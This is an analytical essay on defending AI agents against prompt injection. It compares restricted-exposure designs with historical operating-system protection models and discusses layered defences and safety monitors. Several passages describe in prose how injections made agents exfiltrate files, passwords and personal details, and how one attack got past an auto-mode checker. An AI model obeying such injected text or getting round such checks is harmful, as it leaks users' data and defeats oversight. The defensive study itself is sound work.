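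Better models therefore substantially reduce the loss on tasks the restriction permits. The best evidence is from Prudentia, where the gap to a basic agent with unlimited approvals fell from 30 points with GPT-4o to zero with GPT-5. With FIDES, the gap narrowed only from 22 points to 15 over the same models, so a good model also needs a system that gives it the policies. None of these tests used the strongest models of late 2026. Those models should make fewer mistakes with variables, but they will also raise the unprotected agent's score on tasks that a restricted agent is not allowed to do.

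### Tokens, money and time

Restricted agents also use more computation. Kolluri and colleagues estimated the cost of AgentDojo tasks from logs. The figures below are for GPT-4o, averaged over the four settings. A turn is one round of the agent's loop.

| Agent | Input tokens | Output tokens | Cost per task | Turns |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic with labels and checks | 2,380 | 314 | 0.7 cents | 3.6 |
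| FIDES | 11,131 | 504 | 2.2 cents | 5.7 |
| Prudentia | 27,655 | 700 | 4.7 cents | 7.1 |

FIDES costs about three times as much as the basic agent, and Prudentia about six times. Most of the extra tokens are input, and providers charge less for input they have already processed and stored, so the cost rises more slowly than the token count. The checks are ordinary code and use no tokens. The extra turns come from questions to the quarantined model and, in Prudentia, from the plans it writes before opening a variable.

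Kolluri and colleagues did not record how long each task took, but they say that the time closely follows the number of turns. By that measure, a user of Prudentia waits about twice as long as a user of the basic agent. On WASP, the two agents took almost the same number of turns because Prudentia rarely had to find out what hidden text contained. With o4-mini, Prudentia averaged 6.0 turns on GitLab and 8.1 on Reddit, compared with 5.6 and 8.4 for the basic agent.

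Neither system was built to be efficient. FIDES sends the quarantined model one question at a time and makes one tool call at a time, and Costa and colleagues suggest grouping the questions and running independent calls in parallel. Kolluri and colleagues think training could replace the long instructions that Prudentia sends with every request. Other kinds of defence also commonly need extra computation. Wang and colleagues found this in 33 of the 41 defences they reviewed.

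## How does it compare with rings and security levels in operating systems?

Operating system designers faced a similar trade-off half a century ago. By 1970, people from different organisations were sharing large computers and running programs that others had written. The system had to stop a borrowed program from damaging its user's files, and stop a program with access to secret files from copying them to where anyone could read them. Many restrictions on agents come from the rules of that period. Those rules relied on hardware checks and precise specifications, which have no equivalent inside a language model's context.

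### Rings and gates

Multics was a shared computer system that MIT helped develop. *A Hardware Architecture for Implementing Protection Rings* (Schroeder and Saltzer, 1972) describes how a new Multics processor would enforce *protection rings*. A running program has a ring number from 0 to 7. Ring 0 has the most privileges, and each higher-numbered ring has a subset of the privileges of the ring numbered one lower.

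Multics divides memory into segments, each containing a program or a set of data. Every segment has flags that permit or forbid reading, writing and execution (running the contents as a program). It also has numbers that limit each permission to certain rings. Suppose a mail archive allows reading from rings 0 to 5, writing from rings 0 to 4 and no execution. A program in ring 5 can read the archive but can't change it, and no program can run an email as code. The processor checks these values every time a program uses the segment.

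In Multics, the most basic parts of the *supervisor*, the system's privileged core, run in ring 0, and ordinary user programs run in ring 4. A user can run an untrusted borrowed program in ring 5, and a teacher can test students' programs in ring 6, where those programs cannot call the supervisor. In an agent, the quarantined model is like a student's program, the planning model is like an ordinary user program, and the code that runs tools and policy checks is like the supervisor.

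A program in an outer ring sometimes needs a service that only an inner ring can provide. It can enter the inner ring only at a *gate*, one of a fixed list of starting points in the inner program. If it could start anywhere, it might skip the code that checks the request.

The inner program also has to check the caller's arguments. Suppose a user's program in ring 4 calls a ring 0 program to print the text at the memory address of the password table. The ring 0 program is allowed to read the table, so without that check it would print the passwords. Security researchers call a program that misuses its privileges on someone else's behalf a *confused deputy*. *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) compares prompt injection to this problem, because a hijacked agent uses the user's permissions for the attacker.

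The Multics processor prevents the trick by calculating an "effective ring" for the access:

```
effective ring = max(current ring,
                     ring recorded with the address,
                     outermost ring that could have altered the stored address)
```

Here the result is 4, because the address came from a ring 4 program. Ring 4 may not read the password table, so the processor blocks the access. The hardware checks each access against the permissions of the least trusted ring that could have influenced the address. Similarly, FIDES gives a tool call the label of the least trusted data that influenced it.

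Calls from an inner ring to an outer one were harder to design. The outer program may not have permission to read the arguments, and it needs a temporary gate for that one return to the inner ring. Schroeder and Saltzer found no simple hardware solution and left these calls to the supervisor.

A planning model makes this kind of call when it queries a quarantined model, since it gives work to something less trusted and waits for the answer. Like the supervisor, the controller copies the email to where the quarantined model can read it and limits what comes back. A constrained output format works like a gate that checks its arguments, because the answer can enter the planning model's context only as, say, "true" or "false".

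Rings cannot protect two programs in the same process from each other, because one always has at least the privileges of the other. An agent that combines one company's mail tool with another company's web tool has this problem if neither company should have to trust the other. Schroeder and Saltzer accepted the limitation because nested rings are easy to understand. They argued that people will trust a protection mechanism only if they can understand it completely, and that complicated mechanisms are often insecure.

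### Rules for keeping secrets

Rings also don't stop a privileged program from revealing secrets, since it may write to data that outer rings can read. Bell and LaPadula (1973), in *Secure Computer Systems*, began to develop a mathematical model of computer security that addressed this. Landwehr, who surveyed such models for the US Naval Research Laboratory in 1981, summarises the developed version in two rules:

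- *No read up*: users may not read information classified above their clearance.
- *No write down*: users may not lower the classification of information.

The second rule means that a program with a Secret file open cannot write to an Unclassified one. This is needed even if the user is honest, because the program might contain a *Trojan horse*, which does something useful while secretly leaking data. Bell (1974) explains in *Secure Computer Systems*, a later volume in the same series, that a program that can read a secret file and write to a less secret one might copy information from the first into the second. The second file's label would then be wrong, and the system could no longer control who saw the secret.

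An agent with an injection in its context poses a similar danger, because it does the user's work while also following someone else's instructions. FIDES applies a version of "no write down" when it requires every recipient of a message to be on the reader list for its contents. In both settings, the rule also blocks harmless messages. An officer reading a Secret file can't write an Unclassified note about lunch, and an agent that has opened a newsletter can't ask a colleague about lunch.

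Bell's 1974 revision partly solved this problem by giving each user a current level, which can be lower than their clearance. An officer cleared for Secret can work at the Unclassified level and write the note, but can't open Secret files while doing so. The equivalent for an agent is to start a new session with an empty context.

Bell also found that labels had to cover more than the contents of files. A file's name may itself be secret, so the directory that lists it needs a classification too. But users without clearance can't reach an Unclassified file in a Secret directory, because they have to go through the directory to find it. Bell therefore required that classifications never decrease from a directory to its files. Agent designers have had similar trouble with file names and tool descriptions.

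### Biba's rules for trust

Biba's model of 1977 reverses these rules to protect data against tampering. One example is a database of road routes that anyone may read, but that military planners depend on in an emergency, so changing it could do great damage. The model therefore gives programs and data separate *integrity levels*, which describe how far people can trust them.

In Biba's *strict* rule, *s* and *t* are programs, *o* is an item of data and *i* is the integrity level. A higher level means more trust, whereas in FIDES a higher label means less.

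```
s may read o     only if  i(s) ≤ i(o)
s may change o   only if  i(o) ≤ i(s)
s may call t     only if  i(t) ≤ i(s)
```

A trusted program therefore cannot read less trusted data, just as a planning model never reads untrusted input. The third line corresponds to the rule that a quarantined model may not call tools.

The rule also protects against tampering through a chain of programs. Suppose program *s*₁ reads file *o*₁ and writes to file *o*₂. The first line requires *i*(*s*₁) ≤ *i*(*o*₁) and the second requires *i*(*o*₂) ≤ *i*(*s*₁), so *i*(*o*₂) ≤ *i*(*o*₁). The same argument applies to each later program in the chain, so information can never reach a file more trusted than the one it came from.

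Biba described several alternatives, and they match agent designs closely:

| Biba's policy | When a trusted program wants to read less trusted data | Counterpart in an agent |
|---|---|---|
| Strict integrity | The system refuses | A planning model that never reads untrusted input |
| Low-water mark | The program reads the data and drops to their level | A tainted context |
| Ring policy | The program reads the data, keeps its level and has to check them itself | An ordinary agent that relies on the model to resist attacks |
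| Low-water-mark audit | The program reads the data, and the system only records possible corruption | A log of where data came from, without policy checks |

The ring policy gets its name from the Multics hardware, which lets inner programs read anything that outer ones can. The comparison shows why a permission system alone doesn't stop prompt injection. Permissions can prevent an email from changing the agent's settings directly, but a privileged agent can still read the email and obey it.

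Under the *low-water-mark* rule, a program's level after reading is the lower of its own level and the data's, or min(*i*(*s*), *i*(*o*)). Under the strict rule, the system refuses to let a program read lower-level data, so the program keeps its level. Both rules give the same protection along a chain of files. But Biba thought the low-water-mark rule behaved badly in practice, because a program could make its own work impossible by reading the wrong file, and could recover only by starting again. Agents with tainted contexts get stuck in the same way.

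Biba recommended the strict rule partly for this reason, although it stops a trusted program from reading a lot of data. FIDES combines the strict rule with the low-water-mark rule. Its planning model effectively works under the strict rule while untrusted data stay in variables, and switches to the low-water-mark rule when it opens one of those variables.

### Denning's lattice

Bell-LaPadula and Biba regulate access to files. In 1976, Dorothy Denning proposed regulating the movement of information instead. In her model, every piece of data belongs to a class, and information may flow from one class to another only if a fixed ordering of the classes allows it. Landwehr points out that this approach can track information through a program's individual variables, which access rules for whole files cannot do.

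The ordering forms a *lattice*, which means that any two classes have a lowest class above both of them and a highest class below both. Military classifications are a good example. They combine a level, such as Confidential or Secret, with a set of compartments for particular subjects. One classification is at least as high as another only if its level is at least as high and its compartments include all of the other's. Suppose a report combines information from two documents:

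```
(Secret, {missiles}) ⊔ (Confidential, {ships}) = (Secret, {missiles, ships})
```

Neither document is classified above the other, but the report needs the higher level and both compartments, so a reader cleared for Secret but only for the missile compartment can't open it. Sandhu's *Lattice-Based Access Control Models* presents Denning's axioms as the theoretical basis for this family of security models. Costa and colleagues also require the labels in FIDES to form a lattice. Otherwise, the software would have no well-defined label for an email that quotes two sources.

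The focus on information flow also exposed leaks that access rules miss. Landwehr describes Jonathan Millen's example of a system that obeyed both Bell-LaPadula rules but still leaked information through the code it returned when it refused a request. If a secret determines whether the system refuses, the refusal reveals something about the secret. CaMeL's retry loop leaks information in a very similar way.

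The other leak in CaMeL, which comes from a branch the program does not take, is just as old. Garby and colleagues trace it to work by Fenton, which Denning translated into an ordinary program. Other researchers rediscovered the leak decades later. Agent developers can therefore save some trouble by testing new systems against the old catalogue of leaks.

### Least privilege and complete mediation

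The designers of Multics also drew more general lessons. A 1975 paper by Saltzer and Schroeder is the standard source for two of them. *Least privilege* means giving each program and user only the permissions needed for the job. *Complete mediation* means checking every access to every protected object.

Least privilege is harder to apply to an agent than to an ordinary program. A program that prints invoices does the same job every day, so an administrator can work out once which files it needs. An assistant's job changes with every request, so fixed permissions have to cover everything a user might ask for. An attacker who injects instructions then has access to far more than any single request requires. Chrome tries to solve this by working out a new list of permitted sites for each task.

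Complete mediation in operating systems led to the *security kernel*, an idea Landwehr credits to Roger Schell. The kernel is a small part of the system that checks every access by the programs it controls. It must work correctly, and those programs must not be able to tamper with it. In an agent, the code that runs tools can play this role because the model has no other way to act. But the code has to cover every route by which data can leave, including image links in the agent's answers.

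### What a processor can check and a context cannot

The strongest of these protections has no counterpart inside a language model. A Multics processor tracks the current ring and the segment a program is using, so it can block a single forbidden access while the program runs. It can also block the execution of a segment that contains only data. A model's context has no comparable access controls, only markers that are themselves text, so no component stops an email from influencing the next word.

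Programs can mishandle data too, and conventional attacks often work by making them do so. But programmers can examine a program and sometimes prove that it treats its input correctly. Costa and colleagues describe the behaviour of AI models as random and "weakly specified", so programmers have no comparable proof that a model will treat an email only as information. The boundary therefore has to be outside the model, either before text enters its context or after it proposes an action.

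A boundary outside the model still needs a rule for deciding which actions to allow. A kernel has to check whether the caller may use the memory an argument refers to and whether the function accepts the argument's value. The kernel should also copy the argument before checking it, so that the caller can't change it afterwards. Programmers can specify all of this exactly. For example, if a function accepts file numbers from 1 to 100, the kernel rejects 101.

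Tool calls have specifications too, but these mostly cover the form of the call. Software can easily check that a recipient is a valid email address. It is harder to check that the user wanted to write to that address, because that depends on a request in ordinary language and often on information that the agent finds only while working.

*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* illustrates this with the request "find the quarterly report and send it to Alice". The agent has to take the report's file number from a search result. The same result might contain an instruction to send a copy to an outside address. Using the file number completes the task the user authorised, while sending the copy would add a new one. A rule that bans all information from search results would block both.

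The paper's system, SARA, tries to separate them. One component looks for tool results that suggest actions and records those actions and their arguments. When the agent later proposes a call with real effects, SARA checks for independent support in the user's request and in steps it has already authorised. Repeating an address that first appeared in a suspicious instruction doesn't make it acceptable.

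Attacks succeeded at most 0.63% of the time in SARA's four main test settings on the benchmarks AgentDojo and AgentDyn. This is a strong result, but it isn't the kind of guarantee a processor gives, because SARA has to interpret language to decide what the user authorised, and its designers don't assume that it always does so correctly. They also exclude cases in which the user tells the agent to follow whatever instructions it finds, which is the kind of request that stricter systems can't handle.

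Constrained output formats are an exception because the software can check the output against an exact specification. Landwehr drew a similar distinction in 1981 when discussing programs that remove secrets from documents before release. He doubted that a completely general program was possible, but expected automated methods for highly formatted information within a few years.

### Labels that only rise

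The rules in conventional systems also blocked legitimate work. ADEPT-50, a shared system from the late 1960s that ran at several sites in the Pentagon, gave each session a *high-water mark*, the highest classification of any file opened so far, and applied it to every new file. If someone read a Secret report and then wrote a harmless memo in the same session, the memo was classified Secret.

Landwehr explains that this overclassification was a security problem as well as a nuisance, because when too many files are Secret, people routinely have to lower classifications, and a mistake or deliberate leak is harder to notice among the legitimate changes. Users of agents face the same danger if a tainted context makes them approve dozens of harmless actions a day. ADEPT-50's users nevertheless found the system acceptable to work with, despite its rising labels. Its rules were also looser than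 Bell-LaPadula's and let a Trojan horse copy secrets into an existing Unclassified file.

Stricter systems needed exceptions. Under Bell-LaPadula, no ordinary program can remove the secrets from a document and release the rest, because that means writing to a lower security level, which the second rule forbids. Bell therefore exempted *trusted subjects* from this rule, provided someone had shown that they would not leak information. Landwehr found little guidance in the model on which programs deserved this trust. He thought its main weakness was that it blocked safe operations. Designers could either accept severe limits on what their systems did or rely heavily on trusted programs.

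Agent systems face the same choice. Garby and colleagues found that turning on CaMeL's policy checks halved the share of AgentDojo's banking tasks it completed. Designers can recover some of that loss through endorsements, human approvals and answers in fixed formats, which all let information past the ordinary rules, as trusted subjects did. A short program that checks whether an answer is "true" or "false" deserves such an exemption because anyone can read it to see what it does. Exempting a language model that decides whether an email is safe is much harder to justify, since nobody can give the demonstration that Bell required.

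The trusted part also tended to grow. Landwehr reports that designers found it difficult to gather all the security functions of a general-purpose system into one kernel without making the kernel fairly large and slow. In early Multics, changing rings required extra work by the supervisor, so programmers avoided it. The whole program that controlled typewriter terminals ran in the most privileged ring, although only two of its functions needed special protection. Agent developers may be similarly tempted to let the planning model read a little more if each question to a quarantined model takes time and costs money.

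This history favours narrow restrictions that software makers set up in advance. Microsoft added integrity levels to Windows Vista and ran Internet Explorer at the "Low" level, which was meant to stop an attacker who took over the browser from changing system files. Red Hat Linux used similar controls to separate the servers running on one machine. Most home users never noticed these mechanisms and didn't have to label anything. A browser agent that always keeps web text away from payments would fit this pattern better than a general assistant that requires its user to classify every document.

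The early systems' difficulties are weaker evidence about how much an agent must lose. Landwehr judged from experience, rather than from measured task completion, that most of them were slow, awkward to use or both. Ordinary programs also had few ways to respond when the system refused them access, whereas an agent such as Prudentia can reorganise its work to avoid breaking a rule.

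## Does it replace layered defences?

Rings and security levels rely on a boundary that always holds. *Defence in depth* puts several different safeguards in the way of the same attack, because any one of them may fail. Multics had eight rings, which ranked programs by what they could do, but it had little depth in this sense. A program in ring 4 could call the supervisor in ring 0 directly, so a single faulty gate could give it every privilege on the machine.

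New Zealand's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC-NZ) recommends an "assume compromised" mindset that includes defence in depth, monitoring and an incident response plan. For an agent, restricted exposure is therefore one layer among several. The other layers have to provide protection when the restriction has a gap or when a user needs a task that it rules out.

### The layers around an agent

One common layer is a *sandbox*, a closed environment where the agent's tools can reach only chosen files and network addresses. The table lists the usual layers and what each tends to miss.

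| Layer | What it stops | What gets past it |
|---|---|---|
| Training | Most injected instructions | New kinds of attack, and attacks that contain no instruction |
| Input detectors | Text that resembles known attacks | Text that reads like ordinary business mail |
| Restricted exposure | Outside text that tries to choose the agent's actions | False facts in text that the task has to use |
| Sandbox | Access to other files and networks | Damage inside the sandbox, and leaks through permitted services |
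| Human confirmation | Actions that a person recognises as wrong | Anything that a person approves without reading |
| Monitoring | Repeats of an attack that the operator has noticed | The first attack, and actions that look authorised |

Google's Chrome agent has most of these. Suppose a hostile product review tells the agent to buy a gift card and send the code to a stranger. According to Parker, the instruction would have to get past these defences:

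1. Google trains the planning model on known attacks and directs it to prefer the user's instructions to anything on a page.
2. A classifier checks every page for injections and can block actions based on a page that it flags.
3. The list of permitted sites excludes any site that is irrelevant to the user's task.
4. A second model, the User Alignment Critic, rejects proposed actions that don't serve the user's goal. It sees a description of each action but no unfiltered web content.
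5. The agent tries to pause for the user's permission before it pays for anything or sends a message.

If an attack succeeds anyway, Google can send out a fix through Chrome's automatic updates.

### Three layers that each miss 5%

Suppose an agent has three layers, A, B and C, and each misses 5% of attacks. The share that gets past all of them depends on how often each layer misses the attacks that have already beaten the others:

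```
P(all miss) = P(A misses)
              × P(B misses, given that A missed)
              × P(C misses, given that A and B missed)
```

If the failures are independent, each factor is 0.05 and the product is 0.000125. Only 0.0125% of attacks succeed, or 1 in 8,000. If the same attacks beat every layer, the second and third factors are 1, and 5% succeed. The difference is a factor of 400. (The rate could also be zero, if every attack that one layer misses is caught by another.)

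Even a small overlap in the attacks that the layers miss can greatly raise the combined failure rate. Suppose 1% of attacks beat all three layers because of a shared weakness, and the layers fail independently on the rest. If each layer still misses 5% of attacks overall, about 1.01% get through all three, which is 80 times the rate if all their failures were independent.

An attacker who adapts pushes the result towards the bad case by looking for texts that beat every layer at once. A miss rate doesn't account for this search, because it describes a fixed collection of attacks. Even if the layers are independent and together miss only 1 attack in 8,000, someone trying random attacks has a 50% chance of success after about 5,500 attempts, which is feasible for an automated search. Once a text has beaten all the layers, the 1-in-8,000 figure no longer applies to copies of it, though the layers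 may behave a little differently from run to run.

### Weak defences against altered images

Researchers studied this problem in image classifiers before agents existed. One defence, *feature squeezing*, simplifies an image to remove changes that an attacker may have made. Reducing the number of colours removes small changes to many pixels, and smoothing the image removes large changes to a few pixels. The system then classifies the original and simplified versions and raises an alarm if the answers differ too much. Its inventors reported 99.74% detection accuracy on a set of handwritten digits, half of them altered by attackers who did not take the defence into account.

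He, Wei and colleagues (2017), in *Adversarial Example Defenses*, attacked feature squeezing with full knowledge of how it worked. Their program searched for an altered image that the classifier got wrong and that passed the detector's consistency check. It found one for every test image. The table gives the average size of the changes, measured as the square root of the sum of squared pixel changes, with pixel values from 0 to 1.

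| Defence | Handwritten digits | Small colour photographs |
|---|---|---|
| None | 1.38 | 0.21 |
| Smoothing | 1.57 | 0.21 |
| Fewer colours | 3.86 | 0.95 |
| Both, with the detector | 4.76 | 0.60 |

On the digits, the attacker had to make changes only 23% larger to beat the combined defence than to beat colour reduction alone. On the photographs, the combination was easier to beat than colour reduction alone. Sharma and Chen (2018), in *Bypassing Feature Squeezing by Increasing Adversary Strength*, later got past the combined detector by running existing attacks at stronger settings.

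He and colleagues also combined three detectors designed separately by different teams, and raised an alarm if any one of them did. The size of the change an attacker needed grew from 0.11 to 0.18, which was still too small to see. This was partly because the detectors had similar weaknesses. Images made to fool one detector alone also fooled a second 96% of the time and the third 43%.

Feature squeezing, like the narrow channels between a quarantined model and a planning model, reduces what an attacker can send, but it leaves the attacker far more room. A 28-by-28-pixel image of a handwritten digit in pure black and white still carries up to 784 bits, more than four times as much as a 30-character function name.

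The result only partly applies to agents. The attackers had complete access to small classifiers, and every layer had the same job, judging a picture. An agent's layers can do different jobs. For example, a sentence that deceives a detector has no effect on a rule that blocks all network traffic.

Even detectors fail separately if they are different enough and the attacker has targeted only one. In *Beyond Pattern Matching*, Munirathinam (2026) wrote 20 attacks to evade a detector that looks for sudden changes in writing style. That detector caught none, but a stack of several kinds of detector caught all 20. The test is very small, and its attacks, unlike those of He and colleagues, were not adapted to the whole stack.

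### Keeping hostile text away from the checker

Developers can also make failures more independent by restricting what each layer reads. Chrome's critic works this way, and so does auto mode in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. In auto mode, a second model approves or blocks the agent's riskier actions in place of the user. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that this second model sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not tool results or the agent's explanations. If a file tells the agent to post the user's passwords to a website, the second model sees the attempt to post them and no request from the user to do so. It doesn't see the file's text or a hijacked agent's justification, so neither can persuade it to approve the action.

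The missing information makes some actions harder to judge. If the agent tries to cancel "job abc123", the checker can't determine whether the agent found that ID in a search or made it up. In Anthropic's tests, the checker blocked 0.4% of 10,000 harmless actions and missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to steal data. It also missed 17% of 52 real cases in which the agent had gone beyond what its user wanted. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the checker flagged the danger but wrongly treated the user as having consented.

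The value of a second layer of defence depends on how many of the attacks that get past the first layer it stops. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) includes a test by an outside firm, Trajectory Labs, that allows this to be calculated for a rival product. Injections succeeded 19.03% of the time against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol with full access, and 5.83% of the time with OpenAI's own automatic reviewer switched on, so the reviewer let through roughly 31% of the attacks that had worked on the model alone. With auto mode, none of 720 attempts succeeded against three Claude models. But those attacks succeeded only about 0.09% of the time against Claude without the extra safeguards, so there were almost no successful attacks on which to test the second layer. Anthropic paid for the test, and OpenAI had updated its reviewer by the time the results came out.

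Three weeks later, the security researcher Johann Rehberger published an attack on auto mode that reportedly worked 80% of the time. According to Willison, the agent downloaded and unpacked an archive, then ran some ordinary-looking Python code. The archive contained a file with the same name as a standard Python component, so the code loaded the attacker's file instead. The model never obeyed a hostile instruction, so there was nothing for an injection detector to find. In a few runs, the agent noticed the malicious program and tried to stop it, but auto mode blocked the command.

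### When people approve everything

Human confirmation can serve as a last layer because a person doesn't share a language model's weaknesses, but people who see one request after another stop reading them, a problem known as *approval fatigue*. Claude Code's users approve 97% of requests for permission. By itself this is weak evidence of fatigue, since most of the commands are harmless, but the same users reject 39% of the plans that the agent presents for approval. They apparently pay attention when they have one substantial decision to make.

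Anthropic's strongest evidence comes from an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, who worked on coding tasks without knowing what the study measured. At some point in each session, a clearly dangerous command replaced the text of one request. Testers refused it 143 times (13.6%), while auto mode's checker blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Testers refused about 17% of these commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

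Anthropic also reports how often the two disagreed, which is enough to work out the overlap between their failures:

| | Checker blocked | Checker allowed |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

The checker alone missed 116 commands. Adding the human would have reduced that to 110, because testers caught 6 of them. At the rate they caught commands in the whole set, they would have caught about 16. The commands that got past the checker were evidently harder for people to recognise too, so the failures were not independent.

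These testers weren't risking their own files and may have been less careful than real users. Anthropic also has a commercial reason to show that its agent can work without interruptions. Still, the decline over a session fits ordinary use, where a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission checks bypassed. The earlier comparisons that count approvals assume that users never make mistakes, which on this evidence is much too generous once requests become frequent.

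### Who relies on layers, and why

Willison (2025) argues that 99% is a failing grade in security because an attacker will find the remaining 1%. He was answering an article in *The Economist* that urged AI engineers to think like Victorian builders, who built in redundancy because they could not trust the quality of their iron. The comparison breaks down because attackers, unlike bad iron, search for the weakest point. In his view, the only reliable protection against the lethal trifecta is to remove one of its three features. When OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, described the defence in depth around the Atlas browser, Willison worried that the phrase created a false sense of security (*Dane Stuckey (OpenAI CISO) on prompt injection risks for ChatGPT Atlas*, 2025).

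Companies that sell general-purpose agents can't follow this advice everywhere without removing features their customers pay for. A browser agent has to carry information from one site to another, for example to fill a shopping cart with the ingredients in a recipe. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* makes the same point about coding agents, which are of limited use without access to files, a command line and a network.

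The developers don't claim that detectors are enough. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), input filters usually miss fully developed attacks. One of its examples is a polite email about a company restructuring, which asks the reader's assistant to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". The email worked in 50% of tests on ChatGPT in 2025. To stop it, a filter would have to recognise a lie, often without the necessary context. OpenAI compares an agent to a customer service employee who will sometimes be deceived, so the employer uses software to limit how much money the employee can refund.

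Google combines fixed rules with classifiers and a model trained to resist attacks. In *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, Gavish (2026) says that indirect prompt injection requires ongoing work rather than a one-time fix. Engineers can change the fixed rules soon after discovering an attack, while retraining a model takes longer. Google also simulates attacks with and without a defence, which is the right way to find out what each layer adds, but Gavish gives no results.

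Anthropic comes closest to Willison. It advises developers to contain the agent's environment first and steer the model's behaviour second, because no protection inside the model will be 100% effective. They still disagree about tasks that need untrusted text, private data and a way to send data out all at once. Willison would refuse to automate these tasks, while the developers accept some risk.

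Government bodies mostly stress limiting the damage. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), puts fixed limits on the system's actions first, then measures that make injection harder, then monitoring. He warns buyers about products that claim to stop prompt injection, and adds that a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk may be a poor use for a language model. He also recommends that a model processing somebody's text should drop to that person's privileges. This restates Biba's low-water-mark rule and has the same drawback.

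Later guidance takes a similar approach. In spring 2026, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Publishes Guidance on Securing Agentic AI Use*, the NCSC told organisations that an agent is not ready for deployment if they cannot understand, monitor or contain its actions. In August, after several incidents in which AI models acted without permission, it issued interim advice. Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems* summarises that advice as sandboxing, human oversight and tightly controlled access. These measures are layered, but they are largely meant to limit the harm from a failure.

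### What each covers for the other

Willison's objection is convincing against a stack of models that all judge the same text, but weaker against a stack that includes a hard limit. Hard limits need other defences too, because people make mistakes designing them.

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work, could send data only to approved addresses, including Anthropic's own service, which the product can't run without. Researchers hid instructions in a file, along with a key to an account they controlled. The agent followed the instructions and uploaded the user's files to that account. The sandbox allowed the upload because the destination was on the approved list. Anthropic now blocks requests that carry any key except the one issued to that copy of the product.

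Claude's chat product had a similar gap. To prevent leaks through web addresses, it could open only addresses that came from the user, a search, or a page it had already opened. A researcher built a site with a separate link for each letter of the alphabet and told the model to spell out the user's name by following the links. Willison reports that this attack revealed the user's name, home city and employer until Anthropic closed the gap. In both cases, a model that refused the instruction would have prevented the theft even though the restriction failed. Attackers can also exploit a gap in a fixed rule every time until somebody notices it, so monitoring matters more for these rules than their reliability suggests.

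| Risk | Effect of restricted exposure | What can cover the rest |
|---|---|---|
| An email tries to choose the agent's actions | Stops it | Training and a sandbox, in case of a gap |
| An invoice contains a false account number | None, if the payment may use the invoice | Comparison with a trusted record, or a limit on amounts |
| A task requires following outside instructions | Rules the task out | If the developer allows it anyway, all the other layers |
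| The user pastes in an attacker's text | None, if the system trusts the user | A sandbox without secrets or open network access |
| The agent oversteps with no attacker involved | Little | Checks on actions, and a sandbox |

In February 2026, Anthropic tested pasted text on its own staff. A researcher persuaded an employee by email to run a prompt that looked like routine setup work but also told Claude Code to send away the employee's cloud passwords. The agent complied in 24 of 25 repetitions. Its safeguards check actions against what the user wants, and here the user had supplied the instruction, so only limits on file access and network traffic would have helped.

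Restriction in turn makes human confirmation more useful. When Anthropic put Claude Code in a sandbox, permission requests fell by 84%. A session with 50 requests would then have 8, which would keep the user in the range where testers caught 17% of dangerous commands rather than 5%. Catching 17% is still poor, so it may help more to ask people about whole plans or single important facts, such as the account number on an invoice.

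One layer can also interfere with another. Cowork's sandbox was a sealed virtual machine, a simulated computer inside the real one, and it shut out the security software that companies use to monitor their employees' computers. Administrators could retrieve logs afterwards but couldn't watch the agent live. Even complete logs may not help much, because once an injection has caused an agent to send data through a permitted tool, they show only a successful, authorised request.
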